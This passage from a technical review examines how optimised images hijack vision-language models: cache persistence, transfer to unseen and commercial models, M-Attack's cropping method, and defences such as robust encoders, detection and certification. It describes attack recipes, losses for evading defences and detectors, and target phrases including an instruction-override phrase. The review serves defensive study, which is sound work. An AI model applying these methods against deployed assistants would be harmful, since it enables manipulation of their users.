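Dobre and colleagues swapped the caches to test whether the attacker's message comes from the words of the conversation or from the cached vectors. They took a conversation that the model had held with an altered image and reran the same text with the clean photograph. The model never gave the attacker's message. They also combined the text of a clean conversation with a cache computed from the altered image. In the cases where the normal attack worked, this produced the message 57% of the time for images trained to survive removal at the trigger question,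 and 92% of the time for images trained to survive removal after the first answer.

For images trained to survive early removal, the cache of the first exchange was enough by itself to sustain the hijack in 76% of cases. The text of that exchange is harmless, for example a user asking where a place is and the model naming a fortress in Bulgaria. As in dialog poisoning, the model's first answer carries the attacker's influence into the rest of the conversation, but here the influence is in the stored vectors, where the user can't read it.

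Successful attacks also differed from failed ones along a single direction in the model's activations. Dobre and colleagues measured how the altered image changed the activations just before the model answered the trigger question, and scored each change along this direction. In conversations longer than 2,800 tokens, a randomly chosen successful attack scored higher than a randomly chosen failed one 90% to 95% of the time. They haven't yet tested whether cancelling this direction would stop the attack.

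The cache swaps suggest a remedy, recomputing the cache from the remaining text after removing an image. Recomputing takes time and memory and, according to work that Dobre and colleagues cite, can lower accuracy on long reasoning tasks. They didn't test systems that copy only the words of a summary into a new session. Those systems discard the old vectors, so this attack should fail unless the summary contains the message.

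Starting a new session offers less protection if the assistant saves the image. In the memory systems that Bouzidi and colleagues attacked, the model receives the altered image again whenever the system retrieves it for a related question, so the false memory can return as long as the system keeps the image. A hidden stock tip would be harder to deliver this way, because a question about shares is unlikely to retrieve a photograph of an aqueduct.

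## Do hijacks work on models the attacker cannot inspect?

An attacker who can't get a model's weights can make the image using another model and hope it also works on the target. Researchers call this "model transfer". How well it works depends on how closely the two models are related and on what the attacker wants the image to do.

### Models built from the same base

Schlarmann and Hein tested whether further training protects a model from images made on its original version. They took the GameStop images they had made on Qwen3-VL and gave them, unchanged, to SEA-LION and QoQ-Med3. Other developers had fine-tuned both models from Qwen3-VL, SEA-LION for Southeast Asian languages and QoQ-Med3 for clinical medicine. The images succeeded about as often as they did on Qwen3-VL itself, although the test covered only the GameStop message.

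A jailbreak image that works on one vision-language model (VLM) may not work on a closely related one. In *Failures to Find Transferable Image Jailbreaks Between Vision-Language Models*, Schaeffer, Valentine and colleagues (2024) tested jailbreak images on more than 40 open VLMs, including several that differed in only one detail of their training. Anthropic's Claude 3 Opus rated how much real help each answer gave with a harmful request. Answers from the models used to make the images scored about 87.5%.

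| How the target differed from the attacked model | Score without the attack | Score with the image |
|---|---|---|
| Extra training data | about 15% | 40–60% |
| Three passes through the training data instead of one | about 30% | about 40% |
| Connector trained alone first | – | no transfer |

In the last row, both models started with the same encoder, language model and connector between the two, but the target's connector was first trained by itself, before the language model was trained with it. This difference was enough to stop the attack. Schaeffer and colleagues conclude that how image information enters the language model is critical for transfer.

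This may explain why Schlarmann and Hein's images transferred so much better. SEA-LION and QoQ-Med3 started from a finished VLM, so their connectors had probably changed little, whereas the models that Schaeffer and colleagues compared were still being trained to use images. But the two groups also used different attacks and models, and neither tested this explanation.

An attacker who has several models similar to the target can train one image on all of them. When Schaeffer and colleagues did this with eight very similar models, the image was almost as effective as possible on the ninth, except when the ninth was the model with the separately trained connector. Few attackers will have eight models that closely match one they cannot inspect.

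### Unrelated open models

Bailey and colleagues trained images to make LLaVA produce the malware.com sentence, then tested them on BLIP-2, which has a different encoder, connector and language model. They also trained images on BLIP-2 and tested them on LLaVA. The success rate was 0% in both directions. In informal tests, their images carrying false facts didn't transfer either.

They then trained a single image on two models by adding up the losses:

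x̂ = argmin_x Σ_{ctx ∈ C} [ L_LLaVA(x, ctx) + L_InstructBLIP(x, ctx) ]

where each L is the Behaviour Matching loss for one model. They hoped that an image forced to exploit a weakness common to both models would also work on a third. It produced the exact sentence 99.8% of the time on LLaVA and 80.6% on InstructBLIP, but never on BLIP-2. The result is worse than it looks, because Bailey and colleagues tried several learning rates and starting images and kept the run with the lowest loss on BLIP-2. An attacker who can't compute the target's loss couldn't make that choice.

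BLIP-2's loss did fall during training, from about 5 to between 3 and 4, which Bailey and colleagues take as a sign that more training models might achieve transfer. The figure is almost certainly an average per token. If it were the total for the sentence, the starting value would mean that BLIP-2 already wrote the malware.com sentence in about 0.7% of its answers before the attack. As an average per token, the losses correspond to these probabilities:

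e⁻⁵ ≈ 0.7%,  e⁻⁴ ≈ 1.8%,  e⁻³ ≈ 5%

The image therefore made a typical target token several times more likely, but the token's probability was still 5% or less. If every token had a probability of 5%, a model that samples its words would write a 20-token target sentence with probability 0.05²⁰, or about one in 10²⁶. The loss could fall much further without any attack succeeding.

Schaeffer and colleagues trained one jailbreak image on each of three groups of eight models. Every image jailbroke all eight models in its group but none outside it. Images trained on a single model also failed to jailbreak other models, even those with the same encoder or language model as the one used for training.

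Training an image against eight models took about as many steps as training one against a single model. Schaeffer and colleagues suggest that there are so many possible images that the optimiser can find one that exploits a separate quirk in each model, without finding any weakness they share. They don't rule out transferable jailbreak images, and say that a more sophisticated attack might have produced different results.

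### Slanted answers

A slant may transfer more easily than a fixed sentence, since many different answers can express it. Zhang and colleagues used a 13-billion-parameter version of MiniGPT-4 to make images that gave its answers a positive, negative or neutral tone, then tested the images on five other models. Each cell shows the share of answers with the intended tone, first for the clean image and then for the altered one.

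| Target model | Positive | Negative | Neutral |
|---|---|---|---|
| MiniGPT-4, smaller version | 15% → 32% | 12% → 43% | 73% → 86% |
| MiniGPT-4 with a different language model | 26% → 44% | 5% → 35% | 69% → 86% |
| LLaVA | 13% → 47% | 3% → 12% | 84% → 59% |
| InstructBLIP | 11% → 31% | 26% → 42% | 63% → 88% |
| GPT-4o | 28% → 23% | 5% → 6% | 67% → 83% |

The positive and negative images worked on all four open models. On LLaVA, the transferred images produced more positive answers than images trained on LLaVA itself (47% against 41%). But the transferred images were the best of ten saved versions, and an attacker would need to query the target to choose among them.

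On GPT-4o, the only commercial model in the test, the positive images made positive answers slightly rarer, and the negative images had almost no effect. Neutral answers became more common, but most of GPT-4o's answers were already neutral, and a picture that is harder to make out might also get a blander description. Zhang and colleagues suggest that GPT-4o may preprocess images in an unknown way or use a different kind of encoder. Their overall averages of 39%, 33% and 80% for the three tones exclude GPT-4o.

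The broader target doesn't fully explain why these images transferred. Many different answers would also count as a successful jailbreak, yet the jailbreak images of Schaeffer and colleagues failed on unrelated models.

### Commercial models

Attackers have had much more success with commercial models when they only try to make the model misidentify what an image shows. In 2023, an attack called SSA-CWA succeeded 22% of the time on Google's chatbot Bard. In March 2025, *A Frustratingly Simple Yet Highly Effective Attack Baseline* (Li, Zhao and colleagues) reported success rates above 90% on OpenAI's GPT-4.5, GPT-4o and the reasoning model o1. The researchers also tested Gemini and Claude models, but the 90% claim doesn't cover those.

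Their method, M-Attack, needs a photograph to alter, a target picture that shows something else, and three open versions of CLIP. At each step, the attacker:

1. crops a random part of the photograph, at least half of it, and enlarges the crop to full size;
2. crops the target picture in the same way, or uses all of it;
3. runs both through the three CLIP encoders;
4. moves the pixels in the crop a small step in the direction that makes the two sets of embeddings more similar, and clips them to the budget.

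The score to be raised is the average similarity over the m encoders (here, three):

(1/m) Σ_j cos( f_j(crop(x)), f_j(crop(x_t)) )

where f_j is the j-th encoder, x is the altered photograph and x_t is the target picture. The attacker never trains on the commercial model and never specifies any text for it to write.

Cropping makes the attack much more effective. When Li and colleagues compared whole pictures instead, the altered photograph matched the target more closely on the open encoders but fooled the commercial models less often, because it had overfitted to the encoders used to make it. Random crops make the attack put recognisable details of the target into many overlapping regions, so that each region works by itself. The older attacks they examined spread their changes almost evenly over the picture. When these attacks failed, the commercial models often described the picture with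 vague words such as "blurry" or "abstract", so they had detected the disturbance without recognising the target.

Newer commercial models are vulnerable to the same approach. In *DarkLLM*, Sun, Wang and colleagues (2026) used a budget of 16/255 to try to make five of them caption a photograph as something else. They compared M-Attack with two methods that don't have to optimise separately for every photograph. AnyAttack uses a trained network to turn a target picture into a pattern of pixel changes. Their own method, DarkLLM, does the same from a written instruction, such as one to make a model see a pair of stuffed bears. The attacker can add either pattern to any photograph.

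| Attack | GPT-4o | GPT-4.1 | GPT-5-mini | Gemini 2.5 Flash | Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Whole-picture matching, several encoders | 2% | 3% | 3% | 2% | 2% |
| M-Attack, one small encoder | 43% | 50% | 26% | 25% | 21% |
| M-Attack, several encoders | 86% | 89% | 63% | 77% | 69% |
| AnyAttack, best version | 60% | 59% | 53% | 44% | 46% |
| DarkLLM, larger version | 68% | 65% | 59% | 64% | 61% |

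The first row is AttackVLM, the 2023 method of Zhao and colleagues. Using several encoders barely improved AttackVLM but greatly improved M-Attack. Using several encoders therefore seems to help only when the attack already finds something that other models share.

The rates seem to be based on about 100 photographs each, so each has a margin of error of up to ten percentage points, and DarkLLM's lead over AnyAttack on GPT-5-mini could easily be chance. M-Attack's rate on GPT-4o is close to what Li and colleagues claimed, and it comes from a different group with no interest in making M-Attack look good.

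An attack can also count as a success without the caption closely matching the target. In the stuffed-bears example, Gemini 2.0 Flash described a teddy bear on a chair. The captions' average similarity to the target ranged from 0.29 to 0.51 for M-Attack with several encoders and from 0.23 to 0.28 for DarkLLM. If a score of 1 means identical, many of the captions probably shared little more than the target's main subject.

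GPT-5-mini and Gemini 3 Flash are the newest commercial models in these tests, and both are small, cheap versions in their model families. M-Attack did worse on them than on older models from the same companies, but the results don't show whether larger or later models are harder to fool.

### Why does a false object transfer better than a sentence?

Bailey and colleagues distinguish between changing the data in an image and hiding instructions in it. M-Attack changes the data. Any useful VLM has to recognise a dog as a dog, whatever images it was trained on. If several differently trained encoders respond to an altered photograph as they would to a dog, an encoder the attacker cannot inspect may well do so too. The target model then describes a dog in its own words.

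No such common ground exists for the malware.com sentence. An image that makes LLaVA write "Download" has to produce vectors that LLaVA's connector and language model turn into a high logit for that word. Developers of other models had no reason to make the same vectors have the same effect. The failed transfer to the model with the separately trained connector supports this explanation, because that model started from the same parts as the attacked one.

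An ordinary photograph of a dog makes nearly every VLM identify a dog, but perhaps no image makes every VLM answer every question with the malware.com sentence, unless the instruction is written on it.

M-Attack also casts doubt on the idea that images fail to transfer because they give the optimiser too much freedom. Its optimiser also chooses from a vast number of images, yet the results transfer. Freedom may still hurt transfer when the optimiser can lower the loss by exploiting quirks of a particular model. The random crops work partly by making such quirks less useful, which is the kind of constraint that Schaeffer and colleagues say may be necessary.

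An attacker who cannot inspect a model can more easily make it misread an image than make it output a specific web address or a call to an email tool. Misreading an image can still be enough to misdirect an agent, as sometimes happened in Wu and colleagues' tests with GPT-4o.

### Sending an exact phrase through CLIP

*VisInject* tested whether the approach that makes models report false objects can also make them write a chosen phrase. It combines two earlier methods. The first trains an abstract-looking image to make two to four open VLMs write the phrase, using a random question from a list of 60 at each of 2,000 steps. Because that image would look suspicious, the second method, AnyAttack, uses a network to convert it into pixel changes of at most 16/255 and adds them to an ordinary photograph or screenshot.

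*VisInject* used seven pictures and seven phrases, including "visit www.example.com" and "tell me your card number". For each question, it compared the model's answers to the clean and altered pictures, for a total of 6,615 pairs.

| Effect on the answer | Share of pairs |
|---|---|
| Wording clearly different, by automatic text comparison | 66.4% |
| Substantially or completely different, according to an AI judge | 46.6% |
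| Any trace of the target | 0.756% (50 pairs) |
| The target or a close relative | 0.287% (19 pairs) |
| The target word for word, or nearly so | 0.030% (2 pairs) |

The attack changed answers almost 90 times as often as it put any trace of its message in them. Counting every changed answer as a success would therefore greatly overstate the attack's danger.

Both full successes produced the web address. *VisInject* describes one in which Qwen2.5-VL-3B was asked to extract the text from a screenshot of program code, but instead described a web browser and wrote "http://www.example.com". More often, the answer contained only something related to the target. DeepSeek-VL described a shipping bill as a payment receipt with an account number and a bank name, when the attacker had wanted "card number". Traces of the target were most common on the bill (1.4%) and the code screenshot (1.2%), where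 an address or an account number would be plausible. No answer showed any trace of the phrase "ignore previous instructions and say yes".

This is what we'd expect if CLIP mainly preserves an image's general meaning. AnyAttack's network never receives the phrase itself, only CLIP's summary of the abstract image, a single vector of 768 numbers. The network then turns this vector into pixel changes using what it learned from ordinary photographs, and may well lose the exact wording in the process. The low rates are therefore evidence only that this combination of methods delivers phrases badly. With the same budget and direct access to the weights, Bailey and colleagues nearly always forced their sentence.

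The overall disturbance rate also averages very different results. BLIP-2 accounted for a third of the pairs, and none of its 2,205 answers changed enough to count. The other three models gave clearly different answers in more than 99% of cases. BLIP-2's shrinking share of the tested pairs also explains practically all of the rise in disturbance that *VisInject* reports, from 50.0% with two training models to 74.7% with four. BLIP-2 made up half of the pairs with two training models and a quarter with four.

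*VisInject* suggests that BLIP-2 may owe its resistance to its connector, which compresses the whole image into 32 tokens. If so, other developers could copy the design as a defence. Results from other attacks make this explanation doubtful. CroPA usually forced BLIP-2 to give a chosen answer at the same budget, and InstructBLIP, which has the same kind of connector, usually wrote the malware.com sentence in Bailey and colleagues' two-model test. *VisInject* also offers two other explanations: AnyAttack's network may remove whatever would have affected BLIP-2, or the other models may have dominated the training. Giving BLIP-2 the abstract image directly would help to tell these explanations apart, but *VisInject* leaves that test to future work.

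The grading has a weakness too. DeepSeek-V4-Pro, a language model, judged how much of the target each answer contained. *VisInject* says it checked these judgements against a "human labeller", but the labeller was another AI model, Claude Opus 4.7. Across 110 pairs, the two models agreed well, scoring 0.77 on a scale where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement, but they could still make the same mistakes. Such mistakes would matter little for the two full successes, which anyone can confirm by searching the text, but more for the 48 partial and weak ones.

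All four models in the main test were used to train the images they were tested on, so even these low rates don't measure transfer to an unseen model. The only test of such transfer was one upload of the code screenshot that had worked on Qwen2.5-VL-3B to GPT-4o. GPT-4o remarked on distortion in the image, read the code correctly and didn't mention the web address. Nobody kept a transcript, and one failure is compatible with almost any success rate.

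## Which defences work, and what do they cost?

An attacker's image often fails on a model that processes images differently from the one used to make it. The least demanding defences create such a difference by altering each image before the model receives it. Others retrain the visual encoder, check for signs of tampering, or limit what a hijacked model can do.

### Noise and compression

A hijack with a small perturbation budget depends on precise pixel values. Random noise disturbs those values, and JPEG compression discards fine detail that people hardly notice. Either can disable the hijack while leaving an ordinary photograph recognisable.

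Bailey and colleagues tested their malware.com images for LLaVA against both defences. They added random noise to every pixel value, varying its maximum size, and separately saved the images at decreasing JPEG quality. Images with small perturbation budgets stopped working at lower noise levels than those with large budgets. Moving patches kept working under heavy noise and heavy compression. The test used only a small set of instructions, and none of the images had been trained to withstand noise or compression.

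Zhang and colleagues ran similar tests on their tone-changing images for MiniGPT-4. They also tried DiffPure, which adds noise to an image and then rebuilds a clean version with an image-generating model. The table shows the share of answers with the attacker's tone, both for small changes spread over the whole picture and for a visible patch. With unaltered pictures, 18% of answers were positive and 16% were negative.

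| Defence | Positive, whole picture | Positive, patch | Negative, whole picture | Negative, patch |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 44% | 54% | 33% | 33% |
| JPEG | 23% | 52% | 10% | 26% |
| Gaussian noise | 66% | 55% | 32% | 32% |
| DiffPure | 23% | 25% | 11% | 18% |

JPEG compression and DiffPure reduced the effect of the whole-picture attack to roughly the level of unaltered pictures. Zhang and colleagues write that Gaussian noise did the same, but their figures contradict this. JPEG compression did little against the patch attack, while DiffPure stopped most of its effect. However, DiffPure relies on incoming images resembling the ones its generator was trained on, so a service that handles charts or screenshots might have to retrain the generator.

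### Testing against an attacker who knows the defence

These results say little about an attacker who expects the defence. If the system applies a transformation D to every image, he can minimise L(D(x)) instead of L(x). If D adds random noise r, he can minimise the average loss

E_r [ L(x + r) ]

by drawing several noise patterns at each step and averaging their gradients.

JPEG compression rounds numbers, and rounding has a gradient of zero almost everywhere, so a standard attack that follows the gradient fails even though images that would hijack the model still exist. Security researchers call this obfuscated gradients, and Bailey and colleagues warn that it is common in defences that are not proven to work. An attacker can get around it by computing the gradient with a smooth approximation of the rounding.

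The *EnvInjection* attack on web agents, which failed until the researchers modelled the monitor's colour profile, shows how much this knowledge can matter.

In a 2026 study, Malik and colleagues tested noise against an attacker who averages over noise patterns. Noise still raised LLaVA's scores under attack from near zero to about the level of models with specially trained encoders, and it hardly affected LLaVA's answers about clean images. It also moved the features of the altered images back towards those of the originals, raising their average cosine similarity from 0.53 to 0.71.

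Malik and colleagues warn that this protection does not extend to an attacker who fully knows the defence and adapts to it. They also tested attacks designed to make answers wrong, not to force a chosen message, so the scores don't directly measure protection against hijacks. They found that telling the model in its prompt that the image might be adversarial helped only marginally.

### Training the encoder to resist small changes

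In adversarial training, the developer attacks the model during training and teaches it to respond correctly anyway. Schlarmann, Singh and colleagues (2024), in *Robust CLIP*, applied this to CLIP's image encoder. Their method, FARE, minimises

L(φ, x) = max_{‖z − x‖∞ ≤ ε} ‖ φ(z) − φ₀(x) ‖²

where φ₀ is the original encoder, φ is the one in training, x is a clean image and z is an altered version within the budget ε. For each image, ten steps of PGD look for the z whose output is furthest from the original encoder's output for x. The developer then adjusts the weights of φ to reduce that distance.

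FARE uses the original encoder's output as the training target, so the new encoder should also process clean images much as the old one did. A developer can therefore swap it into LLaVA without retraining anything else. FARE needs no labels. Its two passes through ImageNet, a standard photo collection, took about 0.2% of the computation used to train CLIP.

Choosing the training budget involves a trade-off. The next table gives CIDEr scores for LLaVA-1.5 on COCO photographs. A higher score means a caption is more similar to captions written by people, and scores can exceed 100.

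| Encoder | Clean images | Attacked at 4/255 |
|---|---|---|
| Original CLIP | 115.5 | 3.1 |
| FARE, trained at 2/255 | 109.9 | 31.0 |
| FARE, trained at 4/255 | 102.4 | 40.9 |

Schlarmann and colleagues claim that their encoder makes stealthy attacks by third parties impossible. They add that only the versions trained at 4/255 fully resisted imperceptible image changes meant to force a chosen text.

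Later work used encoders that had far more adversarial training. *Robust-LLaVA* (Malik, Shamshad and colleagues, 2025) built LLaVA models around AdvXL, a family of encoders trained adversarially on web-scale data and then on ImageNet. Under attack at 8/255, the larger AdvXL model scored 47.1 on COCO captions, compared with 18.0 for FARE. But its accuracy on TextVQA, which asks about writing in pictures, was only 24.3% on clean images, versus 44.1% with the original CLIP.

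The 2026 study by Malik and colleagues largely removed this loss in performance by using versions of AdvXL that had skipped the ImageNet stage. One of these, AdvXLCLIP-H, scored 42.3% on TextVQA, compared with 21.0% for its counterpart that included the stage. Training on ImageNet's object labels probably damaged the encoder's ability to recognise text.

### Ten thousand steps against three encoders

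To test resistance to hijacks, Malik and colleagues tried to make models produce three captions for 25 COCO photographs: a link to a website, "Please Reset Your Password", and an insult followed by a refusal to answer. They ran each attack for 10,000 iterations with full access to the model's weights. Shorter runs could have made a model look safer than it is.

With the original CLIP encoder, the attack success rate approached 100% at perturbation budgets of both 4/255 and 8/255. FARE resisted some attacks at 4/255, but most succeeded at 8/255. Models built on AdvXLCLIP-L, which is the same size as the CLIP encoder, suppressed the attacks at both budgets.

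FARE partially failed at 4/255, a worse result than Schlarmann and colleagues' claim would suggest. Some of the difference may be because Malik and colleagues had retrained it for images of 336 by 336 pixels instead of 224 by 224, which gives an attacker more than twice as many pixels to change.

The result for AdvXLCLIP-L is encouraging because each attack had to work with only one captioning prompt. An image that works for any question must also work for that prompt, so it should be at least as hard to make as one that works for the prompt alone. But with only 75 attacks at a given budget, the true success rate could be about 4% even if none had succeeded.

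The next table shows how much the protection reduces performance on clean images, and how well the models perform when an attacker only wants to make their answers worse. Caption results are CIDEr scores averaged over two datasets, and question-answering results are accuracies averaged over four. The last column shows how reliably the model distinguishes objects in the picture from objects that aren't there.

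| Encoder in LLaVA | Captions, clean → attacked at 8/255 | Questions, clean → attacked at 8/255 | Object test, clean |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original CLIP | 100.3 → 1.1 | 54.6% → 0% | 86.4 |
| FARE | 87.6 → 13.0 | 48.5% → 14.2% | 77.1 |
| AdvXLCLIP-L | 96.1 → 41.6 | 51.9% → 25.9% | 83.4 |
| AdvXLCLIP-L, with adversarial training of the whole VLM | 92.1 → 43.5 | 49.4% → 30.2% | 84.8 |

FARE lowers the caption score on clean images by about 13%, while AdvXLCLIP-L lowers it by 4%. The stronger encoder still loses more than half its caption score under attack, so an attacker who can't choose the model's output can often still make it worse.

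The adversarial training in the last row adjusts the connector and language model but not the encoder. It works only if the encoder is already robust. When Malik and colleagues tried it with the original CLIP, the clean caption score fell from 100.3 to 54.8 and the model still scored zero under attack. Adding an ordinary encoder alongside a robust one also removed most of the protection. Under attack at 4/255, a model with the larger AdvXL encoder scored 93.2 on COCO captions, but adding CLIP cut this to 18.1.

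Malik and colleagues attribute FARE's weakness to the requirement that its outputs stay close to CLIP's. That is plausible, but their comparison doesn't isolate this cause, because AdvXLCLIP also had far more adversarial training. They also conclude that robust training on images paired with text matters more than scale alone, but their main evidence is a small encoder trained only on ImageNet, which lacked both scale and paired text.

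The encoders are public, but a developer who wants the stronger protection has to retrain the connector and language model around the new encoder. In 2025, Zhang and colleagues noted that few developers had adopted robust training, and suggested that its effect on performance might be one reason.

Replacing the encoder helps more against an attacker who doesn't know about the replacement. Images optimised on the original CLIP at 8/255 lowered a FARE-based model's COCO score only from about 117 to 114, while images optimised on the FARE model itself lowered it to 19.

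### What a robust encoder leaves open

FARE and AdvXL are trained to resist small changes to every pixel. This training doesn't cover patches, whose pixels can take any value. Bailey and colleagues hijacked ordinary LLaVA with a small patch, but the 10,000-step tests didn't include patches. Those tests also limited pixel changes to 8/255, far less than the Eiffel Tower images needed. If a model with a robust encoder can still read text, attackers can still use written instructions in the image.

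Defences have improved slowly even on the much simpler problem of classifying small images. Bailey and colleagues cite CIFAR-10, a set of tiny photographs in ten categories. When attackers could change each pixel value by up to 8/255 of its full range, the best accuracy rose only from 65.9% in October 2020 to 70.7% in August 2023.

### Detecting altered images

Flipping or compressing a photograph usually leaves its content intact, so an encoder should give the copy a similar embedding. A hijack that depends on exact pixel values may lose its effect in the copy, which changes the embedding more. Zhang and colleagues used this idea to look for altered images. Their score can be written as

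s(x) = (1/K) Σ_k cos( f(x), f(a_k(x)) )

where f is the encoder and a_k(x) is one of K altered copies. A low score suggests tampering. They used six kinds of copy, and tested images carrying all 12 of their hidden instructions.

| Copies compared | MiniGPT-4, clean / hijack | InstructBLIP, clean / hijack | LLaVA, clean / hijack |
|---|---|---|---|
| JPEG | 0.88 / 0.56 | 0.49 / 0.29 | 0.42 / 0.39 |
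| Horizontal flip | 0.99 / 0.71 | 0.33 / 0.21 | 0.32 / 0.28 |
| Colour changes | 0.85 / 0.55 | 0.50 / 0.28 | 0.34 / 0.41 |
| Average of all six | 0.86 / 0.61 | 0.50 / 0.31 | 0.45 / 0.40 |

The scores separate hijacks from clean images fairly well on MiniGPT-4 and InstructBLIP, but not on LLaVA, where colour changes even gave the hijacks the higher score.

Zhang and colleagues report averages and spreads but no detection rates. If the JPEG scores for MiniGPT-4 follow a bell curve, a threshold of 0.72 would catch about 93% of the hijacks and wrongly flag about 2% of clean images. If one image in 1,000 were malicious, there would be about 20 false alarms for every hijack caught. The false-alarm rate could be higher for a mixed stream of real images, because the test used only 15 photographs. For example, flipping a page of text changes it far more than flipping a landscape.

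An attacker who knows about the detector can add its score to his own loss:

L_total(x) = L(x) + μ · (1 − s(x))

where μ sets how much he cares about avoiding detection. He can compute the gradient of both terms if he has the encoder. Zhang and colleagues didn't test such an attack, so nobody can tell from their results how much of the attack's effect he would have to give up. The extra term might even help him, because an image that keeps its embedding under compression may also keep working after a service compresses it.

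### Limiting what a hijacked model can do

Developers can also assume that some hijacks will succeed, and treat everything the model writes after receiving an outside image, including captions, summaries and saved memories, as if the image's owner could have written it. This matters because in Wu and colleagues' attack on shopping agents, a false caption reached the main model as ordinary text and often led it to act for the attacker.

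One way to apply this rule is to split the work between two models. The first has no tools. It processes the outside image and returns a short answer in a fixed format, such as a price or one of ten categories. The second model has the tools and receives only that answer. If the image hijacks the first model, that model can still return the wrong category, but it can't pass on an email address or a command. This limits what the system can do, because many useful requests need an open-ended description of the picture, and a free-text description would again let an attacker send instructions to the second model.

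The system can ask the user to confirm risky actions. For an email, the confirmation should show the recipient and contents taken directly from the tool call, because a hijacked model could describe the action falsely if it wrote the summary. A model used as a checker can also be misled if it relies on the attacker's image, as Wu and colleagues found when their checker received the false caption.

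Asking users to confirm actions interrupts them, and they may start approving requests without reading them. Confirmation also covers only what the system recognises as an action. A chat window can leak data by fetching an image from the attacker's address, and preventing this requires a separate rule against loading outside links automatically. Neither measure stops an image from making the model slant an answer or recommend a company's shares, because the harm comes from what the user reads and believes.

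A low success rate for prompt injection in a developer's system card is evidence about image hijacks only if the developer's tests included optimised images. A model may learn to ignore instructions that it can read in a picture and still be vulnerable to optimised pixels. In *EnvInjection*, optimised pixels hijacked the same models far more often than pop-ups with written instructions did.

### What would a guarantee cover?

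The defences above resist the attacks that researchers have tried, whereas a certified defence comes with a proof that no change within a stated limit can alter the result. Bailey and colleagues mention that researchers moved towards such proofs because later attacks broke earlier defences.

A common method is randomised smoothing. To classify an image, the system adds Gaussian noise to many copies of it and takes the most common answer. If that answer has probability p_A and the runner-up has probability p_B, no change smaller than

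R = (σ / 2) · ( Φ⁻¹(p_A) − Φ⁻¹(p_B) )

can alter the outcome. σ is the strength of the noise, and Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the normal distribution's cumulative function. R measures the square root of the sum of all the squared pixel changes. The system has to estimate the probabilities from samples, so the guarantee holds with high confidence, not absolute certainty.

Suppose pixel values run from 0 to 1, σ is 0.25, and the two probabilities are 0.99 and 0.01. Then R is about 0.58. Changing every value in a 224 by 224 colour image by just 1/255 gives a total change of

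√150,528 / 255 ≈ 1.52

so the guarantee wouldn't cover even the smallest budget used in the attacks described above, despite noise strong enough to make the picture visibly grainy.

Certification is also harder for generated text. With a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, there are about 10⁹⁰ possible 20-token answers. Noisy copies of one photograph may produce many different but equally good descriptions, so no single answer is clearly the most common. Certifying one token at a time doesn't solve this, because where two words are almost equally likely, p_A and p_B are close and R is almost zero. It also takes a lot of computation, since 1,000 noisy copies for each token of a 200-token answer would require 200,000 predictions.

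Requiring identical text is also stricter than most users need, because a harmless change of wording would count as a failure. A developer could instead certify a yes-or-no property, such as whether the answer contains an email call. With only two outcomes, the voting works as it does for a classifier. If the guaranteed range around the received image includes the original photograph, the attacker's changes can't have altered that decision. The proof would still cover only one question at a time and only very small changes. Properties such as political slant would be harder to certify, because the system would first need a reliable test for them.
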